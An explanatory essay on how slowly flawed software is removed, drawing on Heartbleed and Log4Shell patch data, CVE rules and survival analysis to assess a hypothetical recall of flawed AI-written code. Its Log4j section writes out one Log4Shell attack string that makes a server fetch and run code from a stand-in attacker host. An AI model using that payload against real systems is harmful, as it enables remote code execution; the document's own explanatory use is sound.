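# How slowly flawed software is removed, and what that implies for recalling AI-written code

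## What would a recall of AI-written code involve, and how is the removal of flawed software measured?

Programmers now use AI models to write a lot of their code. A programmer describes what the software should do, the model writes the code, and the programmer merges it (adds it to the project's files). Code from one model can end up in thousands of projects whose owners have no connection to one another.

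Suppose the company behind such a model learns of a flaw in the code it writes. When asked for a "forgot my password" page, the model tends to write code that builds reset links from random numbers an attacker can predict, which lets the attacker take over accounts. The company can withdraw the model the same afternoon, but websites that already contain the code will keep sending out predictable links, because the code sits in their owners' files and runs without the model. Removing it would take a recall, meaning a deliberate effort to find, check and, where needed, replace code already in use that came from the flawed model. A carmaker can run a recall because each car has an identification number and a registered owner, but merged code usually has neither.

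Something close to this happened in 2025 with Lovable, a Swedish service that builds websites and apps from plain-language requests. According to Semafor's *The hottest new vibe coding startup Lovable is a sitting duck*, an employee of Replit and a colleague scanned 1,645 apps built with Lovable. They found that 170, about one in ten, let anyone read information about the app's users, including names and email addresses. The proportion is rough, because the scan covered apps that Lovable featured on its own site and came from a competitor. The flaw was also easier to trace than the one in the password example would be, because anyone could find the apps in one place, labeled with the name of the tool.

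### Libraries, versions and public identifiers

Programmers rarely write a whole program themselves, with or without AI. For common jobs, such as encrypting a connection or keeping a log of events, they use a library, which is ready-made software that other programs can use. Each library a program needs is called a dependency. That library may need other libraries, which become transitive dependencies of the program, often without the programmer noticing. Programs fetch libraries from a package registry, a public collection such as Maven Central (for Java), where every library has a name and every release has a version number. If version 2.3 has a flaw, the maintainers publish version 2.4, and anyone can check by name and number whether a program still uses the old version.

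Even when flawed components can be identified by name and number, they take longer to fix the deeper they sit in a chain of dependencies. *Out of Sight, Still at Risk* (2025), a study of Maven dependencies, found that the mean time from a flaw's introduction to its resolution rose from 215 days at the top level to 2,075 days ten levels down.

A vulnerability, a software flaw that an attacker can use, also gets a public identifier. The Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE) Program, a voluntary international effort, gives each publicly disclosed vulnerability an ID and a record describing it. The Lovable flaw, for example, is CVE-2025-48757. According to the CVE Program's *Terminology*, the ID lets different parties and their automated tools confirm that they are referring to the same vulnerability.

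This system works well for libraries but poorly for merged AI-written code. Under the CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), in force since August 25, products that are vulnerable because they share the same code get a single ID. The rules recommend separate IDs when products don't share the vulnerable code or when this is uncertain, and no ID for a flaw in a product that was never publicly available. So a flawed library gets one ID however many programs contain it. If the same model wrote the same password mistake into two websites in somewhat different code, the websites would, on a plain reading, need two IDs, and a company's internal tool with that mistake would get none.

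NVD's *CVE-2025-48757 Detail* (2025), the entry for Lovable in the US government's vulnerability database, instead lists the tool itself as the flawed product and describes how attackers could read or write the databases of its "generated sites". One ID therefore covers the output of a tool. But Lovable disputes the record, arguing that each customer accepts responsibility for protecting their own application's data. A model developer facing a recall could make the same argument, probably more convincingly if its customers had edited the code and run it on their own machines.

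### The steps of remediation and of a recall

Remediation is the whole process of removing a flaw from the systems it affects. *Guide to Enterprise Patch Management Planning* (Souppaya and Scarfone, 2022), published by the US standards agency NIST, describes this process for large organisations. It starts when an organisation learns that a vulnerability affects its systems, and continues through planning, preparing, installing, verifying and monitoring the fix. The table condenses the process into five steps and compares them with a recall.

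| Step | A flawed library version | Flawed code from an AI model |
|---|---|---|
| Learn of the flaw | Maintainers or researchers publish a CVE record with the library's name and versions | Someone notices a pattern in the model's output, then has to reach project owners whom nobody has listed |
| Find affected systems | Search software inventories for the name and version | Search the code itself, or look for records of which code the model wrote |
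| Obtain a fix | Download the corrected version | Write a correction that fits each project |
| Install it | Update the dependency, rebuild and restart | Merge the correction, rebuild and restart |
| Confirm it | Check which version is running | Test the corrected code and look for further copies |

The first difficulty in a recall would most likely be finding the code. In NIST guidance, Souppaya and Scarfone advise organisations to know what software they run "down to the level of packages and libraries". AI-written code lies below that level, inside files that also contain human work. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* (2026), a study of AI-generated code in public projects, notes that programmers often interleave the two and do not always mark their use of AI, which makes it hard to attribute a change to a tool. An inventory could therefore list every package and library and still not help locate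 the AI-written code.

A patch is a change to the code that removes the flaw. For a library, the maintainers write one patch and every user downloads it. In a recall of AI-written code, each project may need its own. One website might store its password-reset links in a database while another sends them through an outside mail service, and a patch that works in one could break the other.

Even an existing patch takes time to install. Organisations may have to test it, wait for a scheduled outage or update other software first. Some equipment must be recertified before anyone may change it. Owners can meanwhile reduce the danger in other ways, such as switching off the password-reset page. But as Souppaya and Scarfone point out, only a patch or an upgrade removes the vulnerability completely while keeping the function.

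Their guide also recommends monitoring after the fix is installed, because someone may restore the unpatched version from a backup. After a recall of AI-written code, the flaw could also return if a programmer later asks a model to rewrite the page and the model makes the same mistake.

### Three kinds of model flaw

How hard the search would be depends a great deal on what is wrong with the model's code.

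Scattered careless errors are the least promising target for a recall. *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026) ran an automated scanner, Semgrep, over 675 security-related pull requests (proposed changes to a project) that AI tools had produced. The scanner reported 853 possible weaknesses. The most common were text-matching rules so inefficient that an attacker could use them to stall a program. Unsafe database and system commands were also common, but the findings covered nearly every major class of weakness. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites a larger count by Schreiber and Tippe, who examined 7,703 files on the code-hosting site GitHub that carried some record of AI authorship. Of these, 12.1% had at least one detectable weakness, and Python files had the highest rates. Scanners raise false alarms and miss real flaws, so neither figure is a count of confirmed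 vulnerabilities. If errors of this sort were the problem, a recall would have nothing specific to look for, and owners might do better to scan all their code, whoever wrote it.

A single repeated pattern, such as the predictable reset link, is much easier to search for. Kordonsky, Levi and colleagues (2026), in *Extracting Recurring Vulnerabilities from Black-Box LLM-Generated Software*, found that each of six coding models repeated its own insecure patterns across different applications. *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code* (2026) also found flaws shared between models. Three models given identical requests for small automation programs produced largely the same classes of flaw, with only three vulnerabilities peculiar to one model. Every program that watched a folder, for instance, had a flaw that could let an attacker reach files outside it. Recalling only one model's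 code could therefore leave the same mistake in code from other models. Searching for the pattern would catch both, and nobody would need to know which model wrote what.

In the worst case, someone might tamper with a model so that it occasionally writes a backdoor, a concealed way into a program, that looks like ordinary code. Scanners search for known patterns, and that person could choose a pattern they miss. The developer might then discover the tampering without learning what to search for, and would have to treat everything the model had written as suspect. The scanner counts above don't measure how often this happens, if it happens at all. Public identifiers might not help either, because the CVE Program allows but does not require its members to treat products that someone has modified to become malicious as vulnerable.

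### Survival curves, half-lives and censoring

Estimating how fast a recall could go requires measuring how fast flawed software has disappeared in the past. Researchers do this with survival analysis, which medical statisticians use to study how long patients live. A survival curve shows the share of flawed systems that remains at each time after a starting date. *Linux Kernel Recency Matters, CVE Severity Doesn't, and History Fades* (2026), which studies flaws in the core of the Linux operating system, defines the curve as the probability S(t) that a vulnerability is still unfixed at time t. The half-life is the time at which the curve first falls to 50%. *Original Sin of npm* (2026) calls this point the median survival time and uses it for flaws in npm, the registry for JavaScript libraries.

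Researchers never see every repair. Some systems are still flawed when the study ends, and others drop out of view earlier, perhaps because their owners have moved them behind a firewall. These systems are called censored. Each one counts for as long as researchers could see it unfixed, but it isn't counted as a repair.

Take ten flawed servers that a researcher watches for a year:

| Month | What happens | Servers in view just before | Share still flawed |
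|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Owners fix 3 | 10 | 7/10 = 70% |
| 2 | 2 drop out of view, still flawed when last seen | 7 | 70% |
| 4 | An owner fixes 1 | 5 | 70% × 4/5 = 56% |
| 8 | An owner fixes 1 | 4 | 56% × 3/4 = 42% |
| 12 | The study ends with 3 still flawed | 3 | 42% |

At each repair, the researcher multiplies the previous share by 1 − d/n, where d is the number of servers that owners fix at that moment and n is the number still unfixed and under observation just before. This is the Kaplan–Meier estimator, the standard method in these studies. The curve passes 50% in month 8, so the half-life is eight months.

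Simpler calculations give different answers. Counting the two vanished servers as fixed gives a half-life of two months, and leaving them out gives four. Averaging the five observed repair times gives three months, even though three servers stayed flawed for a whole year. Those three are the start of the long tail, the part of a population that remains unfixed long after most of it is fixed. The Kaplan–Meier estimate assumes that servers that drop out of view would have been fixed at about the same rate as those that stay in view. If the owners of the vanished servers were unusually careless, its estimate of eight months is too short.

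The answer also depends on what counts as removal. Gurov (2026), in *Mismeasuring the Life of a Line of Code*, tracked 32.5 million line additions in 120 TypeScript projects. Half of the lines were gone within 3.0 years when only deletion counted as removal, and within 1.3 years when moves and rewrites counted too. The longer figure is the safer guide for a recall, because renaming a variable in the password-reset code changes the line but leaves the flaw in place.

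Studies also measure from different starting points. The Linux study counts from when the flaw entered the code, a date that it can only approximate. *The Secret Life of CVEs* (2025) measures how long programmers take to write a patch, with a median of 34 days, and distinguishes this from the delay before the patch reaches users' machines. A patch that is written quickly can still take a very long time to be installed.

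### Downloads, dependent projects, running systems and reachable systems

Any claim that some percentage of something "is still vulnerable" also depends on what the researcher counted. Published figures use at least four quantities, which are easy to confuse.

Downloads of a flawed version are the easiest to count, because registries log them. Sonatype, which sells tools for managing dependencies, reports in *Exploring Unnecessary Risk* that about 13% of 2025 downloads of the logging library Log4j still contained Log4Shell, a flaw for which a fix had been available for almost four years. The share of systems running Log4j that have the flaw can be different, because some systems download the library far more often than others. A project whose automated build downloads it fifty times a day accounts for some 18,000 downloads a year, while a server that downloaded it once in 2021 and has run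 it ever since adds none.

The dependency lists that public projects publish show which of them depend on the flawed version. Some of these projects were abandoned long ago, and others never use the part of the library that contains the flaw. Private projects do not appear in these lists.

Remediation is meant to reduce the number of systems that run the flawed code, but these systems are the hardest to count. One project may run on a single laptop or a million phones, and most companies do not publish what software is on their servers.

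Attackers can reach only some of the systems that run flawed software, and outsiders can sometimes count the reachable ones by scanning the internet. A firewall can reduce this number without removing any flaws. A reachable system also doesn't necessarily cause harm. In Axios' *AI vibe-coding apps leak sensitive data* (2026), the security firm Red Access reported 380,000 publicly accessible apps and other assets built with Lovable and three similar services, of which about 5,000, or a little over 1%, contained sensitive corporate data. Some were public only because of the service's default privacy setting, which is a different problem from flawed code.

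The two most convenient measures of a flawed program's removal are counts of its downloads and of the projects that list it as a dependency, but neither is available for AI-written code unless the code is part of a published library. A recall would have to rely on the number of systems that run the code, which only their owners can establish, and the number that an attacker can reach, which outsiders can estimate if the flaw is detectable remotely. Heartbleed, a 2014 flaw in a widely used encryption library, was detectable remotely, so researchers could track its removal by scanning servers across the internet.

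## How quickly did Heartbleed leave the internet's servers?

Heartbleed was a flaw in OpenSSL, a library that encrypts connections between servers and their users. Either side of a connection can check that the other is still there by sending a short message and asking for it back. The request also includes the message's length, and vulnerable versions of OpenSSL did not check that number against the message's actual length. An attacker could send a single character, claim to have sent 64 kilobytes, and get back the character plus whatever lay next to it in the server's memory. That could include passwords or the server's private key, the secret it uses to prove its identity.

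The OpenSSL project released the first vulnerable version in March 2012. On April 7, 2014, it disclosed the flaw and published a patch that makes the library discard any request that overstates its own length. Server owners had one library to update, a fix from the start, and news coverage that was hard to miss. A specialist told Fortune a year later that Heartbleed had "an exceptionally good patch rate" (Hackett, 2015).

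Outsiders could also check a server for Heartbleed without its owner's help. Durumeric, Kasten and colleagues, in *The Matter of Heartbleed* (2014), sent each server an empty request with a stated length of zero. Correct software ignores this request, while a vulnerable version of OpenSSL answers with a few bytes of random filler. Researchers could safely repeat the test across the whole public internet because the answer showed whether a server was vulnerable without exposing anything from its memory.

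### The first eight weeks

Durumeric and colleagues scanned for Heartbleed from April 9, two days after its disclosure, until June 4. They tested the million most popular websites, as ranked by the traffic-measuring company Alexa, and random 1% samples of all public internet addresses.

"The Matter of Heartbleed" estimates that 24–55% of popular sites using HTTPS, the encrypted form of web traffic, were vulnerable at the start. The researchers had to estimate this because they missed the first two days. For the upper figure, they found that 60% of these sites supported the "are you still there?" feature and that 91% of those ran web-server software known to be affected, which gives about 55%. The lower figure starts from an earlier survey, in which 32.6% of sites supported two newer encryption standards that had arrived in OpenSSL together with the flawed feature. Of those sites, 72.7% ran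 affected web-server software, which gives 23.7%.

By April 9, 11.5% of the popular HTTPS sites were still vulnerable. Even on the lower estimate of how many were vulnerable at first, owners had fixed about half of the vulnerable sites within two days. Owners of the biggest sites acted faster, and Durumeric and colleagues found none of the top 500 vulnerable after 48 hours.

| Share still vulnerable | April 9 | June 4 |
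|---|---|---|
| HTTPS sites among the million most popular | 11.5% | 3.1% |
| All HTTPS servers | 6.0% | 1.9% |

Most of the remaining drop came in roughly the first two weeks, and a few companies accounted for much of it. Ten networks, most of them belonging to hosting or cloud companies, contained over half of all vulnerable servers. Between April 22 and 23, the share of HTTPS servers with the flaw fell from 4.6% to 2.6%, mainly because a handful of hosting companies updated their machines. In a recall, a service that hosts the apps its AI model generates might be able to fix a similarly large share of the flawed code quickly, but nobody could do that for code that customers run on their own machines.

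After that, patching almost stopped. The researchers retested servers that had been vulnerable on April 24 and found that only 0.36% had been fixed by May 1. The true rate was probably a little higher, because they counted only servers that still presented the same certificate (the document that identifies a website) and so missed those whose owners had both updated and changed certificates that week.

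### Graham's three scans

Robert Graham, who runs the security firm Errata Security, scanned the internet three times over the same spring. Errata Security's *600,000 servers vulnerable to heartbleed* (2014) reports that on the night of April 8 he found 615,268 vulnerable systems among some 28.6 million that accepted an encrypted connection. The firm's *300k servers vulnerable to Heartbleed one month later* (2014) reports that the number had fallen to 318,239 by May 8. On June 20 it was 309,197.

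The number of vulnerable systems fell by 48% in the first month. At that rate, about 120,000 would have remained at the third scan, six weeks after the second. Instead, the number barely changed between those two scans. In Errata Security's *300k vulnerable to Heartbleed two months later* (2014), Graham concluded that people had "stopped even trying to patch" and predicted a slow decline over the next decade as owners replaced old equipment.

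Graham's counts have serious limits, which he described himself. In May only 22 million systems accepted an encrypted connection, over 6 million fewer than in April. He suspected that some networks had recognised his probes as attacks and blocked him, or that congestion at his internet provider had lost some of the traffic. He tested only port 443, the standard entry point for encrypted web traffic, so he didn't check mail servers on their usual ports. He also counted internet addresses rather than machines, and one machine can answer at several addresses.

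There is good reason to think the May scan missed a lot. In their full scan of April 24, Durumeric and colleagues found 588,686 vulnerable servers, nearly twice as many as Graham found two weeks later, and their own retest suggests that owners fixed very few in between. If Graham undercounted in May, the collapse in the first month was less dramatic than it looks, and the standstill that followed may have been partly an illusion. (The university team's scanner wasn't perfect either. It recorded an estimated 6.5–10.5% of vulnerable servers as safe because it treated a timed-out test as a pass.)

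Other measurements point to a slow decline over those weeks. The share of all HTTPS servers with the flaw fell by about a quarter, from 2.6% on April 23 to 1.9% on June 4. Austria's computer emergency team, CERT.at, tested servers behind .at web addresses and saw a larger drop over a longer period. Its *Heartbleed in Österreich* (2014) reports that vulnerable web servers fell from 1,850 on April 19 to 740 at the end of July, and vulnerable mail servers from 1,000 to 520. One possible reason for the difference is that a domain name usually belongs to someone who pays for it every year, while a scan of IP addresses also finds forgotten equipment.

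The evidence that removal slowed sharply is strong, but the measured rate for the remaining vulnerable servers depends on who counted and what they counted.

### Why removal slows down

Patching can slow down like this even if no owner becomes less likely to patch over time, as long as some owners are much faster than others. Graham may therefore have been wrong to conclude from the slowdown that people had given up.

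Suppose that owners fixed half of Graham's 615,268 vulnerable systems with a half-life of six days, and never fixed the rest. After 30 days almost all of the first group would be fixed, and the number still vulnerable would hardly change from then on.

| Scan | Graham's count | One constant rate | Half fast, half never fixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| April 8 | 615,268 | 615,268 | 615,268 |
| May 8 | 318,239 | 318,239 | about 317,000 |
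| June 20 | 309,197 | about 120,000 | about 308,000 |

The general version of this model is a mixture of exponential curves:

S(t) = Σ wᵢ e^(−λᵢt)

Here S(t) is the share of systems still vulnerable at time t, wᵢ is the share of systems that started in group i, and λᵢ is the rate at which owners in that group fix them. The wᵢ add to 1, and each group has a half-life of ln 2/λᵢ, or about 0.69/λᵢ. In the example, w is 0.5 for both groups, and λ is about 0.116 per day for the fast group and zero for the slow one. Each group's rate stays constant, but the overall rate drops because slow owners hold a growing share of the systems still vulnerable as fast owners fix theirs.

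The close match in the table is weak evidence for the mixture, because three data points are easy to fit when the groups and rates can be chosen freely, and the counts themselves are unreliable. Fading attention could produce the same curve even if all owners were identical, provided they worked hard in April and moved on to other things in May. The survival curve alone can't distinguish between the two explanations.

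Evidence about the remaining systems partly supports the mixture explanation. Durumeric and colleagues found that 56% of the vulnerable systems in their April 24 scan were embedded devices, meaning computers built into other equipment. They identified more than 70 kinds of affected devices and software packages, including printers, firewalls, security cameras and a point-of-sale system for pizzerias. Many of these devices' owners probably had no way to install a fix at the time. After his six-month scan, Graham told Vice that most of the remaining cases were in connected devices, the "Internet of Things", rather than web servers. Still, some slow owners did act when prompted, as patching increased when the university researchers emailed network operators about their vulnerable servers.

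New vulnerable servers may also have offset some of the repairs. Yngve Pettersen, a developer at Opera Software, ran separate scans and found that 20% of the servers vulnerable in his latest scan had tested clean before, according to Help Net Security's *A month after Heartbleed, many servers are still vulnerable*. He guessed that some administrators, under pressure to do something, had upgraded safe old software to a newer version that still had the flaw. The figure is uncertain because some servers had changed addresses between scans, and Pettersen later withdrew his findings about one brand of equipment because of a measurement problem. The mixture formula does not account for new flawed systems, which could also appear during a recall.

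The mixture matters for a recall because early progress is a poor guide to how the effort will end. If the owners of well-maintained projects replaced a model's flawed code within a week, the model's developer could see a steep drop and expect to nearly finish within a month. But the projects still left by then might be the ones that nobody maintains.

### Replacing the certificates

Updating OpenSSL stopped the leak, but an attacker who had already copied a server's private key could go on impersonating the website. According to lecture notes from NYU, the internet company Cloudflare set up a public challenge and learned that attackers could extract its private keys through Heartbleed.

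Owners therefore also had to generate a new private key, get a new certificate to go with it, and have the old certificate revoked. To revoke a certificate, the company that issued it adds it to a public list of certificates that browsers should reject.

Website owners removed Heartbleed from their servers much faster than they replaced the certificates it could have compromised. Zhang, Choffnes and colleagues, in *Analysis of SSL Certificate Reissues and Revocations in the Wake of Heartbleed* (2014), used roughly weekly scans of the internet to follow certificates for the million most popular domains. They identified 107,712 certificates that Heartbleed could have compromised. By April 30, three weeks after the flaw was disclosed, owners had not replaced 73.3% of them and had not revoked over 87%. By then, only about one in ten of all the certificates the researchers traced to affected servers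 was still on a server with the flaw.

Zhang and colleagues also fitted a curve to the share of certificates not yet revoked, with x as the number of days:

0.179e^(−0.073x) + 0.830

This is the mixture formula with two groups. Owners of about 18% of the certificates revoked them with a half-life of nine or ten days, and the other 83% had a revocation rate of zero. The shares add up to slightly more than 100% because the researchers estimated them from data. The zero rate only means that the curve had flattened within three weeks, so some of those owners may have revoked their certificates later.

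Some owners who replaced a certificate got no benefit because they kept the old private key. Zhang and colleagues found 912 such cases, 4.1% of the replacements they attributed to Heartbleed. Durumeric and colleagues found a higher rate, 14%, among sites that were still vulnerable two days after the disclosure. Only 10.1% of those sites replaced their certificates within the following month, although 73% installed the patch. These numbers are probably worse because the sample leaves out the most diligent owners, who had patched before the first scan.

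Netcraft, an internet security company, found that only 14% of affected sites had replaced the certificate, changed the key and revoked the old certificate, while nearly 57% had neither replaced nor revoked anything. Another 5% had replaced and revoked their certificates but kept the same key. Netcraft considered these the most dangerous cases, since their administrators probably believed they were safe. One was a website of Quebec's public car insurer, whose old certificate was revoked with the reason "keyCompromise".

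Zhang and colleagues asked a few administrators why they had skipped these steps, and seven replied. Some said that their servers held nothing sensitive. Others thought that patching quickly had been enough, even though the flaw had been in OpenSSL for two years before anyone announced it. Seven replies are too few to show how common these reasons were, but the timing of revocations also suggests that the delays came from people. The number of domains revoking certificates dipped every weekend, although most issuers updated their revocation lists at least once a day.

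Unlike merged code, certificates eventually expire even if nobody revokes them. The researchers calculated that if owners never revoked the old certificates they had replaced, about 20% of those would stay valid for at least two more years, and the last would expire around 2020.

A recall could easily require a second step like this. In the password-reset example, an owner who fixed the code would still have to cancel the predictable links already sent and find any accounts that attackers had taken over. Heartbleed suggests that many owners would install the new code and skip this step.

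POODLE, another flaw that became public in 2014, lay in the design of SSL 3.0, a 1990s encryption standard that many servers still accepted so that old browsers could connect. An attacker positioned between a visitor and a website could force the connection down to SSL 3.0 and then decrypt parts of it. Heartbleed was a programming mistake that a library update could correct, but the complete remedy for POODLE was to switch SSL 3.0 off. That risked locking out visitors whose software supported nothing newer, and many servers went on accepting SSL 3.0 for years. Someone recalling AI-written code could face the same reluctance wherever a correction would break something that customers still use.

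### The servers that remain

Later counts of systems vulnerable to Heartbleed come mostly from Shodan, a search engine for devices connected to the internet. It listed about 238,000 in November 2015, 237,539 in March 2016 and roughly 200,000 in January 2017 (Paganini, 2017, *Roughly 200,000 Devices still affected by the Heartbleed vulnerability*).

The latest reliable count appears to be from November 2020, more than six and a half years after the patch came out. Kopriva (2020), in *Heartbleed, BlueKeep and other vulnerabilities that didn't disappear*, searched Shodan and found 204,878 systems listed as vulnerable. He cautioned that Shodan's results aren't always current or accurate, but the small subset he checked by hand mostly matched them. His figure is about two-thirds of Graham's count from June 2014. The two methods differ too much for a precise comparison, but both counts are in the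 hundreds of thousands.

The number was also no lower in 2020 than in early 2017. Owners may have fixed almost nothing in those years, or newly connected devices with old software may have replaced the ones that disappeared. It is impossible to tell which happened from totals alone, because they don't track individual systems.

Anyone could test a server for Heartbleed remotely, but none of these scans could reach servers behind company firewalls, so the vulnerable ones there remained uncounted. In SecurityWeek's *Heartbleed Vulnerability Persists as Patching Lags*, published after Graham's June scan, Trey Ford of the security firm Rapid7 bet that most organisations had a very large number of vulnerable systems on their internal networks.

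## Why is the vulnerable Log4j still in use years after the fix?

Researchers could test the whole internet for Heartbleed, but such tests miss most copies of Log4j, a free library that logs events such as logins and errors for Java programs. Log4j often sits deep inside a larger program, where outsiders can't see it and the program's owner may not know it is there. So estimates of how much flawed Log4j remains come from downloads, the dependency lists of public projects, and companies that scan their customers' applications. The estimates range from under 3% to about 40%, mostly because they measure different things and partly because they date from different years.

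The flaw, called Log4Shell, came from a convenience feature. When Log4j logged text containing an instruction in a particular format, it carried out the instruction, and some instructions made it look something up on another computer. Programs often log text that strangers supply. A website might record each visitor's browser, for instance, and an attacker could send `${jndi:ldap://malicious.example/Exploit}` in place of the browser's name. Log4j would then contact the attacker's server, and Java would download a program from wherever that server pointed and run it. Singh, Yadav and colleagues (2026), in *A Longitudinal Measurement Study of Log4Shell Exploitation from a Reactive Network Telescope*, note that the attacker needed only a program that logged untrusted text and allowed this kind of lookup.

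### Four updates in under three weeks

The volunteers who maintain Log4j accepted the feature in 2013. An engineer at Alibaba reported the flaw privately on November 24, 2021, according to the *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022) by the Cyber Safety Review Board, a US government panel that examined major security incidents. The volunteers developed the fix in public view. On December 9 a Chinese security company posted on WeChat a partly blacked-out picture of a working attack, and the Log4j team released its fix, version 2.15.0, the next day, ahead of schedule. The Board thought it reasonable to suspect that someone had worked out the flaw from a test version of the fix, but couldn't confirm this. A recall of AI-written code would carry the same risk, because telling owners what pattern to search for would also tell attackers.

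The publicity led researchers to look harder at Log4j, and they found more flaws.

| Version | What it fixed | Date of the flaw's public record (2021) |
|---|---|---|
| 2.15.0 | Log4Shell | December 10 |
| 2.16.0 | Another way to run an attacker's code | December 14 |
| 2.17.0 | A way to make the program stop working | December 18 |
| 2.17.1 | A way to run code by changing Log4j's settings file | December 28 |

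Owners who installed each fix as it came out had to update Log4j four times in under three weeks, over the holidays. The Board learned that one US cabinet department had spent 33,000 hours protecting its own networks from the flaw.

The series of fixes also makes later statistics harder to interpret. A program that uses Log4j 2.17.0 is safe from Log4Shell but still has the settings-file flaw, so one source may count it as fixed and another as vulnerable. Some reports also count Log4j 1.x, an older line that never had the feature behind Log4Shell but has serious flaws of its own.

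### Vulnerable downloads

A month after the disclosure, Sonatype, which runs Maven Central, published its first count of vulnerable Log4j downloads. They made up 43% of all Log4j downloads since December 10, ITPro reported in *Nearly half of all Log4j downloads remain critically vulnerable*. By 2025 the share had fallen to about 13%, according to Sonatype's *Unnecessary Risk* (2025).

The vulnerable share of Log4j downloads has fallen sharply, but the number of vulnerable downloads has fallen much less because programs now download Log4j far more often.

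| | First month after disclosure | Average month in 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| All Log4j downloads | just over 10 million | about 25 million |
| Vulnerable share | 43% | about 13% |
| Vulnerable downloads | about 4.3 million | about 3.4 million |

The last figure is approximate because Sonatype has given two totals for 2025. *Unnecessary Risk* puts vulnerable downloads at nearly 40 million, while ITPro's *The open source ecosystem is booming thanks to AI* cites 42 million from a later Sonatype report. The first count may have stopped before the end of the year.

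Both figures are a poor guide to the number of vulnerable systems. Sonatype's *2026 State of the Software Supply Chain* (2026) attributes 86.4% of all Maven Central downloads to three cloud companies. Their customers run automated builds that often start from an empty machine and download every library again. But a company that keeps its own copy of Log4j might download it once and install it in hundreds of programs. Some people also have good reasons to download the old version. Security researchers may need it for tests, and Ilkka Turunen of Sonatype told ITPro that the law sometimes requires companies to be able to rebuild old software.

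The differences between countries are even less reliable. Sonatype found that 29% of Log4j downloads in India and 28% in China were of vulnerable versions in 2025, against 9% in the United States. It located each download by internet address, which may be that of a cloud company's data centre in a different country from the customer.

Sonatype has better access to this data than anyone else, but it has a commercial interest in it. Its one-page summary of the figures, *Log4j in 2025* (2025), also promotes the company's tools for managing libraries. That interest may explain why the company leads with "nearly 40 million" rather than with the fall from 43% to 13%, though it doesn't make the counts wrong.

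Sonatype's figures for other libraries suggest that Log4j users have been comparatively quick to adopt the fix. Almost 58% of 2025 downloads of JDOM2, an XML library, contained a flaw that its maintainers had fixed in 2021. For version 2.6 of Commons Lang, a set of general-purpose tools, the vulnerable share was 99.88% in the months after the fix. Users have to rewrite code to move to the fixed version, because the maintainers replaced the 2.x line with an incompatible one over a decade ago. These libraries are not typical, because Sonatype picked them for their low adoption of fixes. But Log4j had an easy upgrade and worldwide news coverage, which most flawed libraries lack.

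### Log4j in running applications

Companies that scan applications get closer to the number of vulnerable systems. Veracode, a security firm, examined 38,278 applications that used some version of Log4j, from 3,866 organisations, about two years after the disclosure. ITPro's *Log4j* reported the results under a headline about nearly 4,000 organisations that were "still vulnerable". That is roughly the number of organisations with any version of Log4j in the sample, including safe ones. The breakdown by version is more informative:

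| Version in use | Share of applications | Approximate number | Open to Log4Shell? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Versions with Log4Shell | 2.8% | 1,070 | Yes |
| 2.17.0 | 3.8% | 1,450 | No, but has the settings-file flaw |
| 1.2.x | 32% | 12,250 | No, but unsupported since August 2015 |

The three rows add up to almost 39% of applications with some security problem in Log4j, fourteen times the share with Log4Shell itself. The second row probably reflects the rush to update in December 2021. Veracode suspected that many teams updated quickly to get rid of Log4Shell and then stopped paying attention before the last fix.

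A year later, Contrast Security, which monitors applications while they run, found vulnerable versions of Log4j in 12% of Java applications, according to Slater-Robins in *What is the Log4Shell vulnerability?* That is four times the earlier figure, but the two aren't directly comparable because the firms have different customers and Contrast's "vulnerable" versions may include some with other flaws. Both samples also consist of organisations that use a security company's products, so vulnerable versions are likely to be more common in applications that nobody monitors.

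### How quickly maintainers adopted the fix

The maintainers of active projects fixed Log4Shell quickly. *Drop it All or Pick it Up?* (Maeprasart, Ouni and Kula, 2024) examines 53 public Java projects that dealt with the flaw in December 2021. The median fix reached a project's code six days after the disclosure. Fixes had a median of one line added and one deleted, presumably the line that gives Log4j's version number. However, data collection ended on December 27, so the study could not include fixes that took longer than 17 days.

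Tanaka, Yamasaki and colleagues (2025), in *Mining for Lags in Updating Critical Security Threats*, found that 73% of packages had moved to version 2.17.0 or later within three months of its release, and 95% within a year. Packages with frequent releases tended to update sooner. But these percentages appear to cover only the packages that did update, since a package that never switched has no delay to measure. Of the 10,650 packages that had used Log4j's core component at some point, the researchers found 2,210 that switched from an older version to a fixed one. Some of the other 8,440 may never have needed the update, for instance because they adopted Log4j after the fix, so we can't calculate from these numbers what share of the vulnerable packages updated in time.

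*Mitigating Persistence of Open-Source Vulnerabilities in Maven Ecosystem* (2023) includes libraries that were slow to update. It mapped the dependencies among more than 540,000 libraries on Maven Central and identified those that had inherited Log4Shell, directly or through other libraries. A library counted as still affected if its newest version led to a flawed Log4j. By this measure, 65% were still affected after three months and half after 308 days, in October 2022. By then the share was falling increasingly slowly, as one would expect from the mix of fast and slow owners behind the Heartbleed curve.

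A half-life of 308 days is long for a repair that typically takes one line. It also overstates progress, because it counts a library as fixed once its maintainers publish a safe version, even if no one installs it. When the researchers checked public projects on GitHub in April 2023, almost sixteen months after the disclosure, they found 973 that used Log4j's core component. Of these, 392 (40%) had a vulnerable version.

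Most other flaws last longer. The same study covered 1,861 flaws in Java libraries and found that 59% still affected more than half of the libraries downstream. Maintainers had cleared only about 9% completely. *Tracing Vulnerabilities in Maven* (2025) reports a median of 249 days for the 4.5% of cases in which a direct dependent probably had to wait for a patch after the flaw became public. Owners of flawed AI-written code could face the same wait.

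### One fix in a three-level chain

The 308-day figure combines libraries that use Log4j directly with libraries that inherit it through others, and the direct users were faster. An invented example shows why. A hospital runs a billing program that uses a library for printing reports. The report library uses a spreadsheet library, and the spreadsheet library uses Log4j 2.14.1, which has the flaw. The fix then has to travel through every level:

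1. Log4j's maintainers publish version 2.17.1. Nothing changes at the hospital, because the spreadsheet library still asks for 2.14.1.
2. The spreadsheet library's maintainers change the number, test their library and publish a new version. The report library still asks for the old one.
3. The report library's maintainers do the same.
4. The hospital's programmers switch to the new report library, then rebuild, test and restart the billing program.

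If each of the last three steps takes 30 days, the hospital gets the fix after 90 days, even though nobody was especially slow. If 80% of the people responsible at each level act within three months of receiving the fix, as few as 51% (0.8³) of such chains could have the fix all the way through after nine months. If the maintainers of the report library have abandoned it, the fix never reaches the hospital by this route.

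*Mitigating Persistence of Open-Source Vulnerabilities in Maven Ecosystem* found that, across all the flaws it studied, libraries directly above the flawed one, like the spreadsheet library, held up the fix on 35% of affected routes, and libraries further along held it up on 37%. The researchers counted only the first obstacle on each route, starting from the flawed library, so the libraries further along may have been slower than the 37% suggests. Of the new library versions that still contained Log4Shell, 94% had inherited it indirectly.

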